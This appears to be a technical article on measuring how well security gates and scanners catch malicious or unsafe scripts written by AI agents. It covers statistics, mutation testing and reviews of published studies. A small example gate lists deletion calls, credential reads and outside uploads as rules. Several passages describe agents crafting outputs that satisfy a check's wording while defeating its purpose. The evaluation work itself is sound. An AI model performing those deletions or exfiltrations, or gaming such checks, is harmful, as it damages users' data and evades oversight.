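The method uses no approximation, so it also works for small samples and for rates close to 0 or 100%. *Agent Behavioral Contracts II* (2026) explains in its proof that the method is conservative because counts can only be whole numbers.

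### What a perfect score proves

If the gate misses nothing, the lower limit is zero and the upper limit has a simple formula:

upper limit = 1 − 0.025^(1/*n*).

For a gate that blocks all 120 malicious samples, this gives an upper limit of 3.0% on the true miss rate. A gate that misses 3.0% of malicious programs would still block all 120 samples in about one test in forty.

Some papers put the whole 5% on one side and use 0.05 in place of 0.025. The limit for 120 samples is then 2.5%, close to the "rule of three" estimate of 3/*n*. *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove* (2026) uses this version and gets 0.57% for no failures in 520 trials. *Two Conformal Constructions for Adaptive Within-Document AI-Text Screening* (2026) calculates that it takes 2,995 samples without an error to show that a rate is below 0.1%. Either version is fine if the report names the one it uses.

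A gate that blocks no benign programs in a small test may still block some in use. In *Parallax* (2026), a system for checking agents' actions blocked none of 50 legitimate actions at its default setting and 18 at its strictest. For the default setting, the exact 95% interval for the false-block rate extends to 7.1%. At that rate, a gate checking 10,000 benign programs a day would wrongly block about 700.

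The number *n* must count only the samples that could have produced the error being measured. *Bounded Loops* (2026) tested a check on 209 defective and 62 sound samples, and the check accepted none of the defective ones. An earlier version of the paper calculated the upper limit on the rate of wrong acceptances from all 271 samples and got 1.4%. An outside reviewer noticed that a sound sample can't be wrongly accepted, and the corrected limit, based on the 209 defective samples, is 1.8%.

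The formula also assumes independent samples, but programs from the same family are not independent. The held-out part of the small corpus in the last section has 100 malicious programs from 20 families. With a perfect score, the upper limit on the miss rate is 3.6% if each program counts separately, but 16.8% if each family counts once. The family-based limit is safer to report.

A confidence interval, however narrow, applies only to programs like those in the corpus. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) reports no false alarms on 270 benign skills, with an upper limit of 1.4% on the false alarm rate. But the researchers generated these skills for the test, so the limit doesn't extend to real skills, which would be harder, according to the paper, because they routinely start interpreters and use the network. Likewise, the 3.0% upper limit on the miss rate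 for a perfect score on 120 malicious samples doesn't cover kinds of attack missing from the corpus.

### When malicious programs are rare

In the invented run, 94.9% of the refusals were correct. This depends on the mix of samples, one malicious program for every five benign ones, which is far from what a gate meets in service. Suppose that the agent writes 10,000 scripts a day and five of them are malicious. On an average day, the gate then makes

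- 5 × 0.94 = 4.7 correct refusals and
- 9,995 × 0.01 = 100 wrong ones.

Precision falls to 4.5%, although the gate is the same. In general, if a share *π* of all programs is malicious and the gate has block rate *B* and false-block rate *F*,

precision = *πB* / (*πB* + (1 − *π*)*F*).

Ignoring *π* is known as the base-rate fallacy. Stefan Axelsson described its effect on intrusion detection in 2000, and Erbacher (2022), in *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity*, argues that people in the field still lack a clear idea of how low a false alarm rate has to be. For this agent, the formula shows that half of the refusals would be correct at a false-block rate of 0.047%, or about one benign script in 2,100. To show that a gate achieves this rate, a tester would need about 6,400 benign samples with no false blocks, even with the more lenient one-sided limit.

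The false-block rate's interval of 0.5% to 1.8% corresponds to between 48 and 183 wrong refusals a day, while the number of correct refusals stays between 4.5 and 4.8. A builder who wants to know how much work the gate will cause therefore learns more from another thousand benign samples than from another hundred malicious ones.

The gate can still be useful with a precision of 4.5%, because it cuts the number of malicious scripts that run from five a day to about one every three days. Whether this is worth 100 wrong refusals a day depends on how much work they cause. They are tolerable if an agent can rewrite a refused chart script in two seconds, but not if a person has to investigate each one.

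### A separate rate for each kind of harm

Suppose that the 200 malicious samples include 40 that delete or overwrite the user's files, and that all 12 misses are among them:

| Harm | Samples | Blocked | Block rate | Exact 95% interval |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Deletes or overwrites files | 40 | 28 | 70% | 53% to 83% |
| All other harms | 160 | 160 | 100% | 97.7% to 100% |
| Total | 200 | 188 | 94% | 89.8% to 96.9% |

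The 94% total matches neither row, and it changes with the mix of samples in the corpus. With the same gate, it would be 90% if the corpus had twice as many deletions and 96.7% if it had half as many.

In *SkillsMetric*, Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026) tested a static scanner on 266 malicious skills of 16 types, and it detected 62.4% of them. It found 26 of the 28 skills that send data to an outsider but none of the 11 that destroy files or permissions on the host, because those use ordinary calls such as `shutil.rmtree`. Both samples are small, but their exact confidence intervals, 76% to 99% and 0% to 28%, are far apart. The scanner also detected both supply-chain attacks in the set, but the interval for that 100% rate starts at 16%.

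Measuring a block rate for each harm therefore takes more samples than measuring one overall rate. To show a block rate of at least 90% for a single harm, a tester needs 36 independent samples and no misses. The small corpus in the last section holds out only ten programs from two families for most harms. Even if all ten were independent, blocking every one would still be consistent with a miss rate as high as 31%. Each harm's row is still worth reporting because it can reveal that the gate doesn't stop that harm at all.

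Results for the benign twins also need a separate row, because the rarity calculation should use only the false-block rate from the random sample of the agent's output.

### Counting an "ask"

Suppose that some of the refusals in the invented run were really questions to a person:

| Verdict | Malicious | Benign |
|---|---|---|
| Deny | 170 | 3 |
| Ask | 18 | 7 |
| Allow | 12 | 990 |

If every question stops the program, the block rate is 94%. If the person approves everything, it is 85%. In between, it depends on the share *r* of malicious programs that the person rejects when asked:

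effective block rate = (denied + *r* × asked) / all malicious samples.

We can't assume that *r* is close to 1. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts, but this is weak evidence of carelessness because most of the commands were probably safe. Anthropic also ran a controlled study with 1,053 paid testers, in which a dangerous command appeared as a routine prompt during a coding session. The testers caught it 13.6% of the time, and only about 5% after 50 or more earlier prompts. Anthropic used the study to justify replacing these prompts with an automatic check, so it has an interest in the result. With *r* = 0.136, the gate's effective block rate is 86%, barely higher than if the 18 questions had been approvals.

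At 10,000 scripts a day, the seven questions about benign samples would scale to 70 a day. One person answering them all would soon pass the point at which Anthropic's testers were catching almost nothing.

*Jev-Guard* (2026), a gate for agents' actions, treats "ask" and "block" alike in automated runs. A test of such a gate on an unattended agent should count every question as a block, whether the sample is malicious or benign, which here gives a 94% block rate and 1% false blocks. Counting questions as blocks only on malicious samples would lower the reported false blocks to 0.3%, but the gate could achieve both 94% and 0.3% only if a person answered every question correctly.

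Stopping every "ask" can also block benign scripts without preventing any more harm. Jing (2026), in *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know*, tested a gate on 57 harmful and 8 benign shell scripts. When the gate stopped scripts only on "deny", none of the harmful ones took effect and all eight benign ones ran. When it also stopped scripts on "ask", it blocked all eight benign scripts and prevented no further harm. All 532 "ask" verdicts concerned comments and other template lines around the real commands, and once Jing removed these lines, the stricter policy blocked no benign scripts. Merging "ask" with "deny" would have shown a false-block rate of 100% without revealing the cause, so test results should list the counts for the three verdicts separately.

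### Severity thresholds

Scanners usually give each finding a severity, and the builder decides how severe a finding must be for the gate to block a program. Each threshold defines a different gate, with its own block rate and false-block rate.

*SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, July 2026) is a good example. It checks skill files before a coding agent loads them. It searches each file for 530 text patterns and passes any file without a match. If there are matches, it sends the surrounding text to a language model, which labels the file safe, suspicious or malicious and gives a confidence between 0 and 1. By default, SkillGate blocks a file labelled malicious with a confidence of at least 0.7. It quarantines a suspicious file for human review if the confidence is at least 0.5 and only warns if it is lower.

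The researchers tested it on 1,500 real benign files and 150 malicious ones written for the benchmark. They also tested SkillScanner, a scanner from Cisco, at each of its severity levels. Without a language model, SkillScanner gave these results:

| Lowest severity that counts | Block rate | False-block rate |
|---|---|---|
| Info | 82.0% | 86.5% |
| Low | 48.0% | 18.7% |
| Medium | 47.3% | 17.4% |
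| High | 6.7% | 1.3% |
| Critical | 4.7% | 0.6% |

None of the scanner's thresholds would make a good gate. At the lowest, it flagged a larger share of the benign files than of the malicious ones, so refusing files at random would have worked slightly better. Raising the threshold from medium to high removed 242 of 261 false alarms, but also 61 of 71 detections.

A false-block rate means little without the block rate at the same threshold. SkillGate's block rate was 0.769, with about 17 false alarms on the 1,500 benign files. SkillScanner with the same language model had only 11 false alarms, but it flagged just 27 of the 150 malicious files, a block rate of 0.180.

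The false alarms also differed in severity. All 11 of SkillScanner's were critical, so a gate that blocks high and critical findings would have stopped 11 legitimate files. Only about 3 of SkillGate's 17 were that severe, and a gate could send the rest to quarantine. It makes sense to count the blocking alarms separately, because developers notice a blocked installation much more than an entry in a review queue. But *SkillGate* breaks down severities only for benign files. It reports the severe false alarms alongside a block rate of 0.769 that isn't restricted to severe findings, so a gate with a high threshold might stop a smaller share of malicious files.

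The comparison with SkillScanner is also shaky. Yang, Ying and colleagues ran the same version on the same 150 malicious files, blocking at high or critical severity, and measured a block rate of 0.647 without a language model and 0.973 with one. Judging by their scores, the scanner also wrongly blocked about 14% of the benign files when it used a language model. They used a larger model and rebuilt the skills' scripts, which may explain part of the gap. Neither paper fully explains the gap, so the 0.180 applies to one set-up, not to the scanner in general.

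SkillGate reports 17 false alarms, the average of three runs with 7, 24 and 20. The exact intervals for 7 and 24 false alarms in 1,500 files don't overlap, although every run used the same files. The language model's answers had changed, perhaps because its provider updated it during the three weeks of testing. A gate with only fixed rules returns the same verdicts every time. An exact interval accounts only for the uncertainty from the choice of files, so a gate that uses a language model needs several runs, and the report should give the result of each.

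A finding's severity describes how bad the problem would be if the finding were right, not how likely it is to be right. *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026) reports critical findings in 11 skills in its library, and identifies a recurring false alarm in which a skill reads its own access key and calls its own service.

Severity thresholds also cause misses. Yang, Ying and colleagues examined 1,935 misses by rule-only scanners, and in 310 of them the scanner had found the malicious behaviour but rated it too low to block. Recording findings as well as verdicts reveals these cases, which need a different fix from a missing rule. Raising a rule's severity isn't always the right fix, because the rule may also match benign skills. For example, a rule that reports undeclared network access matched 48.3% of the malicious skills but also 29.3% of the benign ones.

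Some scanners add up a score and compare it with a threshold. Chen and colleagues score skills from 0 to 100, with review from 25 and automatic blocking from 45. They chose the lower threshold from the scores of 138,133 public skills, 1.75% of which reached it. Choosing a threshold this way requires no labels and shows how many alarms to expect, but not how many are justified. The highest-scoring skills were mostly legitimate security tools.

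SkillGate's precision also depends on the share of files that are malicious. On its benchmark, where that share is 9.1%, its precision was 87.5%. Yang, Ying and colleagues cite a survey that confirmed 157 malicious skills among 98,380. At that rate, SkillGate would stop about 121 of the malicious skills and raise about 1,100 false alarms, a precision of 10%. *SkillGate* cites a report of 1,184 malicious packages, about a fifth of the skills in one registry. At that rate, its precision would be 94%.

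## Checking that the tests would notice a broken gate

A gate can score perfectly on a corpus if it has one rule for every sample. Held-out samples expose that kind of tuning, but they don't show whether the tests would fail if a rule stopped working. A rule can break when someone shortens a list, reverses a condition or renames a function. If another rule blocks the same samples, the block rate doesn't change, so the tests don't reveal the broken rule.

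Mutation testing looks for this by breaking the gate on purpose. A *mutant* is a copy of the gate with one deliberate defect. The procedure is short:

1. Run the unmodified gate on the working part of the corpus. Set aside the samples it misjudges and record its verdicts and findings on the rest.
2. Make a copy of the gate with one defect, such as a missing rule.
3. Run the copy on the same samples.
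4. If any result differs, the tests have caught the mutant. Otherwise it survives.
5. For each survivor, write a sample on which the intact gate and the broken one disagree.
6. Go back to the intact gate and repeat with the next defect.

*Large Language Models for Multi-Lingual Equivalent Mutant Detection* (2026) defines the mutation score as the number of mutants caught divided by the number of mutants that are not equivalent. Equivalent mutants are excluded because they behave like the original on every input, so no sample can catch them. This can happen when the deleted rule only repeated another one.

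The new samples from step 5 belong in the working part, because whoever writes them has the rules in view.

### A small example

Here is a tiny gate for the sales agent. For each function call in a program, it receives the function's full name and the first argument, with an empty string in place of the argument if it isn't a constant.

```python
DELETE = {"shutil.rmtree", "os.remove"}
COMPANY = "https://backup.example/"

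def findings_for(name, arg):
    found = []
    if name in DELETE:
        found.append("deletes files")
    if name == "open" and "credentials" in arg:
        found.append("opens stored passwords")
    if name == "requests.post" and not arg.startswith(COMPANY):
        found.append("sends data outside the company")
    return found
```

The gate denies a program if any call produces a finding. The corpus has four programs: `average.py`, the backup script that sends a settings file to the company's server, `send.py`, and a script that deletes the report folder with `shutil.rmtree`. The gate allows the first two and denies the others, a perfect score. Five mutants give these results:

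| Defect | Verdict that changes | Findings that change |
|---|---|---|
| `shutil.rmtree` missing from the list | deletion script | deletion script |
| `os.remove` missing from the list | none | none |
| No check on `open` | none | `send.py` |
| No check on `requests.post` | none | `send.py` |
| Every upload refused | backup script | backup script |

Comparing verdicts catches only two of the five mutants. `send.py` breaks two rules, so the gate still denies it when either rule is removed. Comparing findings as well catches four, because removing either rule shortens the list of findings for `send.py`. The last mutant blocks too much, so only a benign program catches it.

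Each mutant that left the verdicts unchanged reveals a sample missing from the corpus. The missing samples are a script that removes a single file with `os.remove`, one that prints the stored passwords without sending them, and one that sends the sales file to an outside address. With these three added, each of the five defects changes a verdict.

### How much a test suite can overlook

In *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean*, Hill (2026) checked the tests for a program he had written, which refuses packages of test results whose files don't support the numbers claimed for them. He disabled the program's 112 refusal statements one at a time. His tests caught 37 of these changes and missed 75, so about two thirds of the statements could each be disabled without any test failing.

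The tests included sixteen tampered packages, made specifically to prove that the program can refuse a package. On their own, they caught 10 of the 112 mutants, and they could not have caught more than 16. When a rule is removed, a malicious sample gets through only if no other rule rejects it, so a test that compares only verdicts can detect the loss of at most one rule per sample. A large corpus in which every sample breaks several rules may therefore be a poor test of any of them. It's worth having at least one sample for each rule that only that rule rejects.

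Hill then fixed four bugs he had found by hand and added a tampered package for each. The fixes introduced seven refusal checks, and the score went from 37 of 112 to 39 of 119. Both additional catches were among the new checks, so the tests covered the old ones no better than before. He next wrote 75 tests, one for each check whose removal had gone unnoticed in the first round, and the score rose to 112 of 119. Much of that gain is guaranteed, as Hill admits, because a test written for one check will fail when that check is missing.

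One run in between scored 119 of 119, but the score was meaningless because two tests had already been failing before Hill changed anything. The test run therefore failed for every mutant, and his tool counted each failure as a catch. This is why the procedure starts with the unmodified gate. Samples that the gate already misjudges can instead hide mutants, because another defect may not change their result. *Text2NGAC* (2026) tested access-control policies with 918 mutants and missed three because they damaged an entry that was already wrong.

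A mutant may also be caught by only a few tests. *Keep the Process, Change the Supplier* (2026) switches off five protections in a system that controls agents' tool calls, and its 43 tests catch all five. One mutant makes 15 tests fail, but two others make only 2 fail each. The paper warns that five mutants are too few to show that the tests are adequate. Reporting the number of failing tests for each mutant helps, because a protection checked by only two tests can become untested if someone deletes or rewrites both.

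#### Choosing the defects

The useful defects to plant in a gate are mostly simple: a deleted rule, a missing list entry, a reversed condition, a "deny" changed to "allow", or an exception that lets a program through. Defects that break everything inflate the score because they are easy to catch. *Runtime Authorization of Self-Generated Subgoals in Long-Horizon Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) therefore ignores defects that merely corrupt an outer hash, and stores each of the others with the smallest case that exposes it and the reason the system should give for refusing that case.

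A language model can look for defects that the tests miss if its prompt includes those tests. Kiele, Saad and Wang (2026), in *Beyond Rule-Based Mutation Testing*, tried this on two sets of programming exercises. They measured the share of mutants that passed the basic tests but failed a much larger set, since failing the larger set confirms that the defect is real. The shares were 87.7% and 79.1% with the basic tests in the prompt, 12.2% and 23.0% without them, and 4.4% and 5.7% for a conventional tool. Nobody has shown the same for gates, but the method should work for them too, since a gate is also a program with a test suite.

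Testing with mutants cannot show that a rule is missing. Hill's program eventually scored 143 of 143, but an outside engineer still found a package that it wrongly accepted.

### Jing's command gate

The most complete published example for a gate is Jing's *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know*, whose results on "ask" verdicts came up earlier. Its gate checks shell commands rather than Python programs. One component turns each command into a structured action that records what the command does, which files it names, which disk zone those files are in, and, if the command starts a program by its path, a hash of that program. Seven rules then determine whether the verdict is allow, ask or deny.

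The gate matches the recorded correct decision for all 61 commands in a frozen table, both when the agent declares beforehand which files it means to touch and when it doesn't. Jing points out that rules tuned to such a table could pass it, and so made 50 mutants of the gate. The tests run on them were the table with 13 additional rows, the gate's own 49-case self-test, and three cases with injected faults. Together they caught 46 of the mutants (92%).

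The four survivors were:

- *A missing privileged tool.* The mutant dropped `su`, which switches to another user, from a list of sensitive commands. No test depended on that entry.
- *The wrong zone.* If one zone lies inside another, the more specific one should decide. The mutant let the broader one decide, and no test path gave a different result.
- *An unresolved link.* The mutant stopped following symbolic links in the paths an agent declares. None of the declared paths in the tests had a link in it.
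- *An uncounted wildcard.* The mutant ignored how many files a wildcard adds to a command and relied on the total number of targets. Whether the tests catch this depends on which files are on the test machine. After the deletion of one decoy file they did, and the score rose to 94%.

The first three are gaps in the corpus, each precise enough to turn into a new test in a few minutes. The fourth means that the score depends on the state of the disk as well as on the gate. So did the perfect score on the table, which fell to 59 of 61 on a disk image that an earlier run had damaged. Jing at first reported a related failure as a defect in the gate.

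#### Comparing reasons as well as verdicts

An earlier round of the study compared only verdicts, so it missed six mutants that changed the reason for a verdict but not the verdict itself. Jing then added 17 probes that also record the reason, and these caught five of the six.

A correct verdict with the wrong reason often means that the intended rule isn't working. Suppose a gate denies a deletion because it couldn't parse the command. When someone improves the parser, that refusal disappears, and the rule that should have caught the deletion may never have worked. The wrong reason also misleads an agent that uses it to revise its code.

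As a further safeguard, Jing's tool for making mutants stores a hash of the gate's source and does not run if the source has changed. Otherwise, after an update to the gate, the tool could make an edit in the wrong place and produce a plausible score that measures something else.

#### Commands from another source

Jing also ran the gate on 216 commands translated from an earlier Windows study, and it agreed with the recorded decision on only 133. The recorded decisions follow Windows rules, so a disagreement does not necessarily mean the gate was wrong. The serious cases are 30 commands that the gate allowed but should have denied according to the record. In 11 of them, the attack was in a document or script that the test had left out, and 9 were translation errors. The other 10 came from differences between the two systems. Only these could be blind spots in the gate, and Jing had predicted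 that there would be none.

#### What happened when the scripts ran

A gate's verdicts alone don't show whether it changes anything on a real machine. Jing therefore ran the 65 scripts from the "ask" verdict test on a disk full of decoy files, with and without the gate, and compared the disk before and after each run. Without the gate, 25 of the 57 harmful scripts had an effect, while with it none did and all eight benign scripts still ran.

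The gate stopped all 57 harmful scripts, but 25 is the fairer count of harms prevented, since the other 32 had no recorded effect even when nothing stopped them. That count is probably slightly too low, because one of those 32 wiped the experiment's own log, destroying 47 rows in a folder the comparison didn't cover.

The result holds only if the gate receives the script's text, not just its file name. Jing's hook opens the file and passes the gate its contents and the folder where the script will run, because relative paths depend on that folder. Jing calls any block based on the file name alone fake.

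For comparison, Jing wrote the same policy as a profile for AppArmor, a Linux feature that limits which files a program can use. With that profile, 8 of the 25 harmful effects still occurred. A profile that lets a program write to a folder can't stop it from destroying the folder's contents.

One person wrote the gate, the test cases and the mutants, so all three may have the same omissions. The gate refused none of the eight benign scripts, but with so small a sample the exact interval for the false-block rate still extends to 37%. The gate models only operations on files, so it doesn't cover a script like `send.py`, whose damage is a network request, and the drop from 25 to zero doesn't measure protection against theft.

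### Paired checks

Even when it is hard to decide the right verdict on a program, it can be easy to tell that two programs deserve the same one. `shutil.rmtree` deletes the report folder whether the script calls it by its full name, through an alias or after importing it directly. A gate that denies two of these and allows the third is wrong somewhere, and the test can show this without labelled samples. The reverse check uses programs that make the same call with different effects. `open` on the sales file is harmless in read mode but destroys the contents in write mode, so a gate that gives both the same verdict is matching only the function name.

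Jing built six small tables of such pairs, 78 rows in total. They showed that a request could get opposite verdicts depending on whether it arrived as a command or as structured data, because two parts of the system interpreted a field differently. The tests also had a defect, because their file format treated the pipe character as a column separator and silently dropped the only row with a piped command. None of the 313 cases from the Windows study had exposed either problem.

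*Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (Mishra, 2026) applies paired checks to scanners that look for passwords and access keys in source code. Mishra generated keys from each scanner rule's pattern and put them into up to twelve ordinary settings, such as a quoted assignment, a configuration file or a function argument. In her own scanner, the right rule fired at least 99.76% of the time in ten of the settings. When the key ended in a hyphen, the rate fell to 52.33%. Five rules were defective, and two of them never fired on keys ending in a hyphen. The scanner missed one in 64 keys of one common type.

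All five rules had passed the project's own tests because every test key was in the same position and ended in a letter or digit. A general fallback rule caught some of the affected keys but reported them as medium severity instead of high or critical. A test that checked only whether the scanner reported anything would have counted those as successes, even though a gate that blocks at high severity would have let them through.

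Two studies of static analysers for ordinary bugs use the same idea. *An Empirical Study of False Negatives and Positives of Static Code Analyzers* (2024) rewrote programs without changing their meaning and found 12 misses and 2 false alarms in three widely used tools. The difficult part is making sure the meaning stays the same, especially if a language model does the rewriting. *StaAgent* (2025) runs the same tests on both versions and keeps a pair only if output, errors and execution traces are identical. For malicious samples, this check has to run on the isolated machine used to confirm their labels.

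A test suite needs harmless inputs as well as harmful ones. In *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture*, Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues (2026) asked a small language model to block or allow 132 attacks and 120 ordinary tool calls from software work. It blocked every attack, so it would have looked like the best check in the study if tested on attacks alone. But it also blocked 118 of the 120 ordinary calls, so an agent whose calls it screened could have done almost nothing.

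### Scores before and after the repair

Hegelich and colleagues compared that model with a list of text patterns and with a fuller gate that resolves paths and network addresses, inspects the first bytes of files and tracks sensitive data.

| Check | Attacks blocked (of 132) | Ordinary calls refused (of 120) |
|---|---|---|
| Text patterns | 58 | 0 |
| Fuller gate, first run | 124 | 0 |
| Fuller gate, after five new rules | 132 | 0 |
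| Small language model | 132 | 118 |

Hegelich and colleagues looked at the eight samples the gate missed in the first run, added five rules and ran it again. They report both results, which many papers don't. Only the first, 93.9%, estimates how the gate would do on new samples. The second run would score 132 of 132 even if each new rule recognised only the exact samples it was written for, so it confirms that the repairs work on those samples but doesn't show whether the gate would block more new attacks. The exact interval they give for the second result, 97.2% to 100%, assumes samples that played no part in shaping the gate, but the eight missed samples were used to write the new rules.

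Even the first result, 93.9%, is probably too favourable, because the researchers designed both the samples and the gate from the same catalogue of attack types. It measures how often the gate catches new examples of attacks they had already listed. However, three of the eight misses were harmless, since they only passed shell text to a program that prints it. Excluding them gives 124 of 129, or 96.1%.

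Samples from people or models that haven't seen the gate make a stricter test. For *Bounded Loops*, five coding agents each read a task's purpose and a correct result, but not the program that checks the results. They then had to write a version that met the task's literal requirements but defeated its purpose, for example by keeping a required heading in a contract and negating the obligation underneath. Their 38 versions exposed 16 defects in the checks. After the repairs, the checks accepted none of the 38, but this score again comes from samples that had guided the repairs.

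### A regression routine

A gate in service will miss things, and each miss is more informative than another invented sample. Whoever maintains the gate can turn it into a permanent test:

1. Save the program exactly as it ran, and confirm its effect on the isolated machine.
2. Cut it down to the shortest version that still does the harm and still passes the gate. Keep both versions.
3. Write a benign twin and two or three other ordinary ways to get the same effect.
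4. Run the new tests before touching the rules. The malicious ones that the gate misses should fail. If none does, the tests don't reproduce the problem.
5. Change the rules and run the whole suite, including every benign program.
6. Remove the new rule in a mutant and check that the suite catches it.

False blocks deserve the same treatment, with the wrongly refused program as a permanent benign test.

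Running the whole suite matters because repairs can cause new faults. Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* describes teams without such tests as stuck in a loop where "fixing one failure creates others". Mishra's first repair fixed all five defective rules but made two of them miss keys followed by a hyphen, which the old versions had caught. The change looked reasonable when she read it, and she found the fault only when she reran the checks with one more setting added. Jing relaxed a rule that had sent every command without a recognisable file target to a person. On the next run over the 216 older commands, the gate wrongly allowed one more command, a recursive deletion whose target it had failed to recognise. The old rule had sent that command to a person only because of the same failure.

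The mutants should run again too, because people tend to add new rules without tests. Hill's score fell from 100% to 97.2% when he added twelve refusal checks, although his tests still caught everything they had caught before. His automatic build now fails if the score drops below 99%. A full run with 143 mutants took under six minutes on a desktop processor.

The gate should always pass the whole regression suite, so that score can't estimate how much new malicious code it would block. The estimate has to come from the held-out part, which becomes less reliable with repeated use even if nobody reads the samples. Suppose a builder tries 20 versions of a gate on the same 100 held-out malicious programs and keeps the one with the best score. If every version actually blocks 90% of such programs and their errors are unrelated, the best will typically score about 95% by luck. The builder should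 instead use the working part to choose a version, run that version once on the held-out part, and publish the result. Before running the next version once in the same way, the builder should replace any held-out families that guided a change with new ones.

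## What published tests of static scanners have found

Most builders will start from an existing scanner. Several research groups have measured how much such scanners catch, mainly using insecure code and malicious packages. A gate for an agent's scripts has to check somewhat different code, so the figures need some interpretation.

### Code that passes Bandit and Semgrep

Pourleyli, Urmi and Melo (2026), in *Beyond Static Guarantees*, measured how often a program still has an exploitable flaw after two scanners have found nothing wrong with it. Of their 1,355 Python samples, 810 came from RedCode, the benchmark of risky programs described earlier. Another 424 came from CyberNative, a dataset of vulnerable code written by language models, and 121 from SecurityEval, a hand-curated set of programming tasks linked to weaknesses in MITRE's list.

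The test had three steps:

1. Bandit and Semgrep scanned every file. One finding of any severity from either tool was enough to flag a file. They flagged 701 files and passed 654.
2. A small language model, GPT-5.4-nano, examined each passed file five times for weaknesses. A weakness became a candidate if the model reported it in at least three of the five runs. This gave 394 candidates in 235 files.
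3. The same model tried to exploit each candidate. It looked up the definition of the weakness and some real cases, wrote a program to attack the file, and ran it in a container without network access. It did this five times per candidate, and three successes counted as confirmation.

The third step confirmed 120 weaknesses in 83 files, or 12.7% of the files that had passed the scan. Another 20 weaknesses had only partial evidence, and counting them brings the total to 95 files, or 14.5%. The model failed to trigger 208 candidates, and 46 attempts were inconclusive.

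So a clean report from both scanners doesn't prove that code is secure. It would be wrong, though, to conclude that one in eight clean scripts from an ordinary agent is exploitable, because most of the confirmed cases come from one dataset:

| Dataset | Samples | Candidates | Confirmed | Share confirmed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RedCode | 810 | 315 | 106 | 33.7% |
| CyberNative | 424 | 42 | 12 | 28.6% |
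| SecurityEval | 121 | 37 | 2 | 5.4% |

RedCode has 30 variants of each scenario, and one scenario is a predictable random seed, so the 29 confirmed cases of weak randomness may mostly be copies of a single flaw. The study also counts two labels for weak randomness separately, so some of these cases could come from the same file.

Pourleyli and colleagues say the overall rate is probably too high for realistic code, since two of the datasets are adversarial or deliberately vulnerable. It could also be too low for the samples they tested, because the model proposed no weakness in 419 of the passed files, so nobody tried to exploit them.

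The confirmations are also uncertain, because the same model proposed the weaknesses and judged whether its attacks had worked. If it misunderstands a weakness in the second step, it may repeat the misunderstanding in the third, and running it five times doesn't help. It confirmed all 29 candidates for weak randomness. Confirming these is easy because it mostly means showing that a program uses an ordinary random number generator instead of a cryptographic one, which the model had already noticed. No human expert checked the verdicts. Pourleyli and colleagues suggest using a second model from a different family, or having people review a sample.

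They also found that the scanners reported nothing for some types of weakness, including CWE-338, one of the two labels for weak randomness. But MITRE lists CWE-338 as a narrower form of the other label, CWE-330, which Bandit did report elsewhere in the collection, so the gap is partly due to labelling.

#### Weaknesses and malicious acts

Of the 120 confirmed weaknesses, 27 let a program use up memory or processor time and 29 are weak randomness, together 47% of the total. Another nine are password hashes that are too easy to crack. These are flaws in programs that aren't malicious, and most of them matter little in a script that runs only once. The model also proposed several cases of code injection, which would be more serious, but confirmed none.

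The method isn't suited to finding malicious code either. It looks for a weakness that an attacker could exploit, but a program that deletes the user's files does harm without being exploited. The container also had no network, so a script like `send.py` could not have delivered its data. For a gate against malicious code, every malicious RedCode program that the scanners passed is a miss, even if the model found no weakness in it.

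The number of such misses would be more useful to a builder than the 12.7%, but the paper doesn't report how many files the scanners flagged in each dataset. Its totals are consistent with the scanners missing anywhere from about a fifth to almost nine tenths of the RedCode samples. Across all three datasets, 48% of the samples passed, although researchers had collected nearly all of them because they were vulnerable or risky. The real miss rate may be higher, since a file counted as flagged even if Bandit had only reported something harmless in it. The study had no benign samples for comparison, so it gives no false-block rate.

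A builder can easily fill this gap. The static scan took 77 seconds for all 1,355 files, or 57 milliseconds each, so the RedCode samples should take less than a minute. The test should leave out the nine scenarios whose code is merely buggy and give each remaining scenario its own row in the results.

The other two steps used 96 million tokens and took 28.7 hours, more than 1,300 times as long as the scan. They averaged over two and a half minutes for each file that had passed. The median attempt to exploit a weakness took 25 seconds, and the slowest took more than 20 minutes. An agent can't wait that long before running each script, but a builder could occasionally use the method on a sample of programs that the gate has allowed.

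### The accuracy of CodeShield

Chennabasappa and colleagues report a precision of 96% and a recall of 79% for CodeShield, citing *CYBERSECEVAL 3* (2024) for the test. Bhatt, Chennabasappa and colleagues had already published the same figures in *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023) for the Insecure Code Detector, the library of rules behind CodeShield. All three papers are from Meta, and they appear to report the same test from 2023.

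At that time, the detector had 189 rules for 50 types of weakness in eight programming languages. To test it, Bhatt and colleagues labelled 50 programs or fragments per language by hand, about 400 in total, all written by language models. By these labels, 96% of the code that the detector flagged was insecure, and it flagged 79% of the insecure code.

The 79% is probably too high for code in general because of how they chose the prompts. They first ran the detector on open-source code to find insecure lines. They then gave a model the ten lines before such a line and let it continue, or asked it to write similar code from a description. The models were therefore likely to produce the kinds of flaw that the detector has rules for. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* found that choosing tasks this way has a large effect for Bandit and Semgrep.

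The results for a single language are also imprecise. If 18 of the 50 samples in one language were insecure and the detector found 14 of them, the exact interval for its recall would run from 52% to 94%.

The 96% precision depends on how common insecure code is, just as a gate's precision depends on how common malicious programs are. In the same paper, the detector flagged about 30% of the code that the models wrote for the test cases. If it flagged the same share of the hand-labelled samples, the two published rates imply that it flagged about 1.9% of the secure ones. At that rate, its precision would fall to 69% for an agent that writes insecure code only 5% of the time.

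Later papers have mostly relied on these figures without checking them. *Give LLMs a Security Course* (2025) uses the detector to decide whether generated code is secure and cites the 96%. *aiXamine* (2025) uses CodeShield for the same purpose because of its "reported high accuracy". *LLM-CSEC* (2025) ran CodeShield on generated C and C++ code and counted its findings, but the count doesn't show how many findings were correct. *PurpCode* (2025) replaced the pattern matching in Meta's benchmark with Amazon's CodeGuru analyser because pattern matching can be inaccurate, but it gives no error rate for either.

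No one seems to have independently repeated the original test. The closest substitute is the test in *STELP*, where CodeShield blocked 68% of the unsafe samples, but that test favoured STELP.

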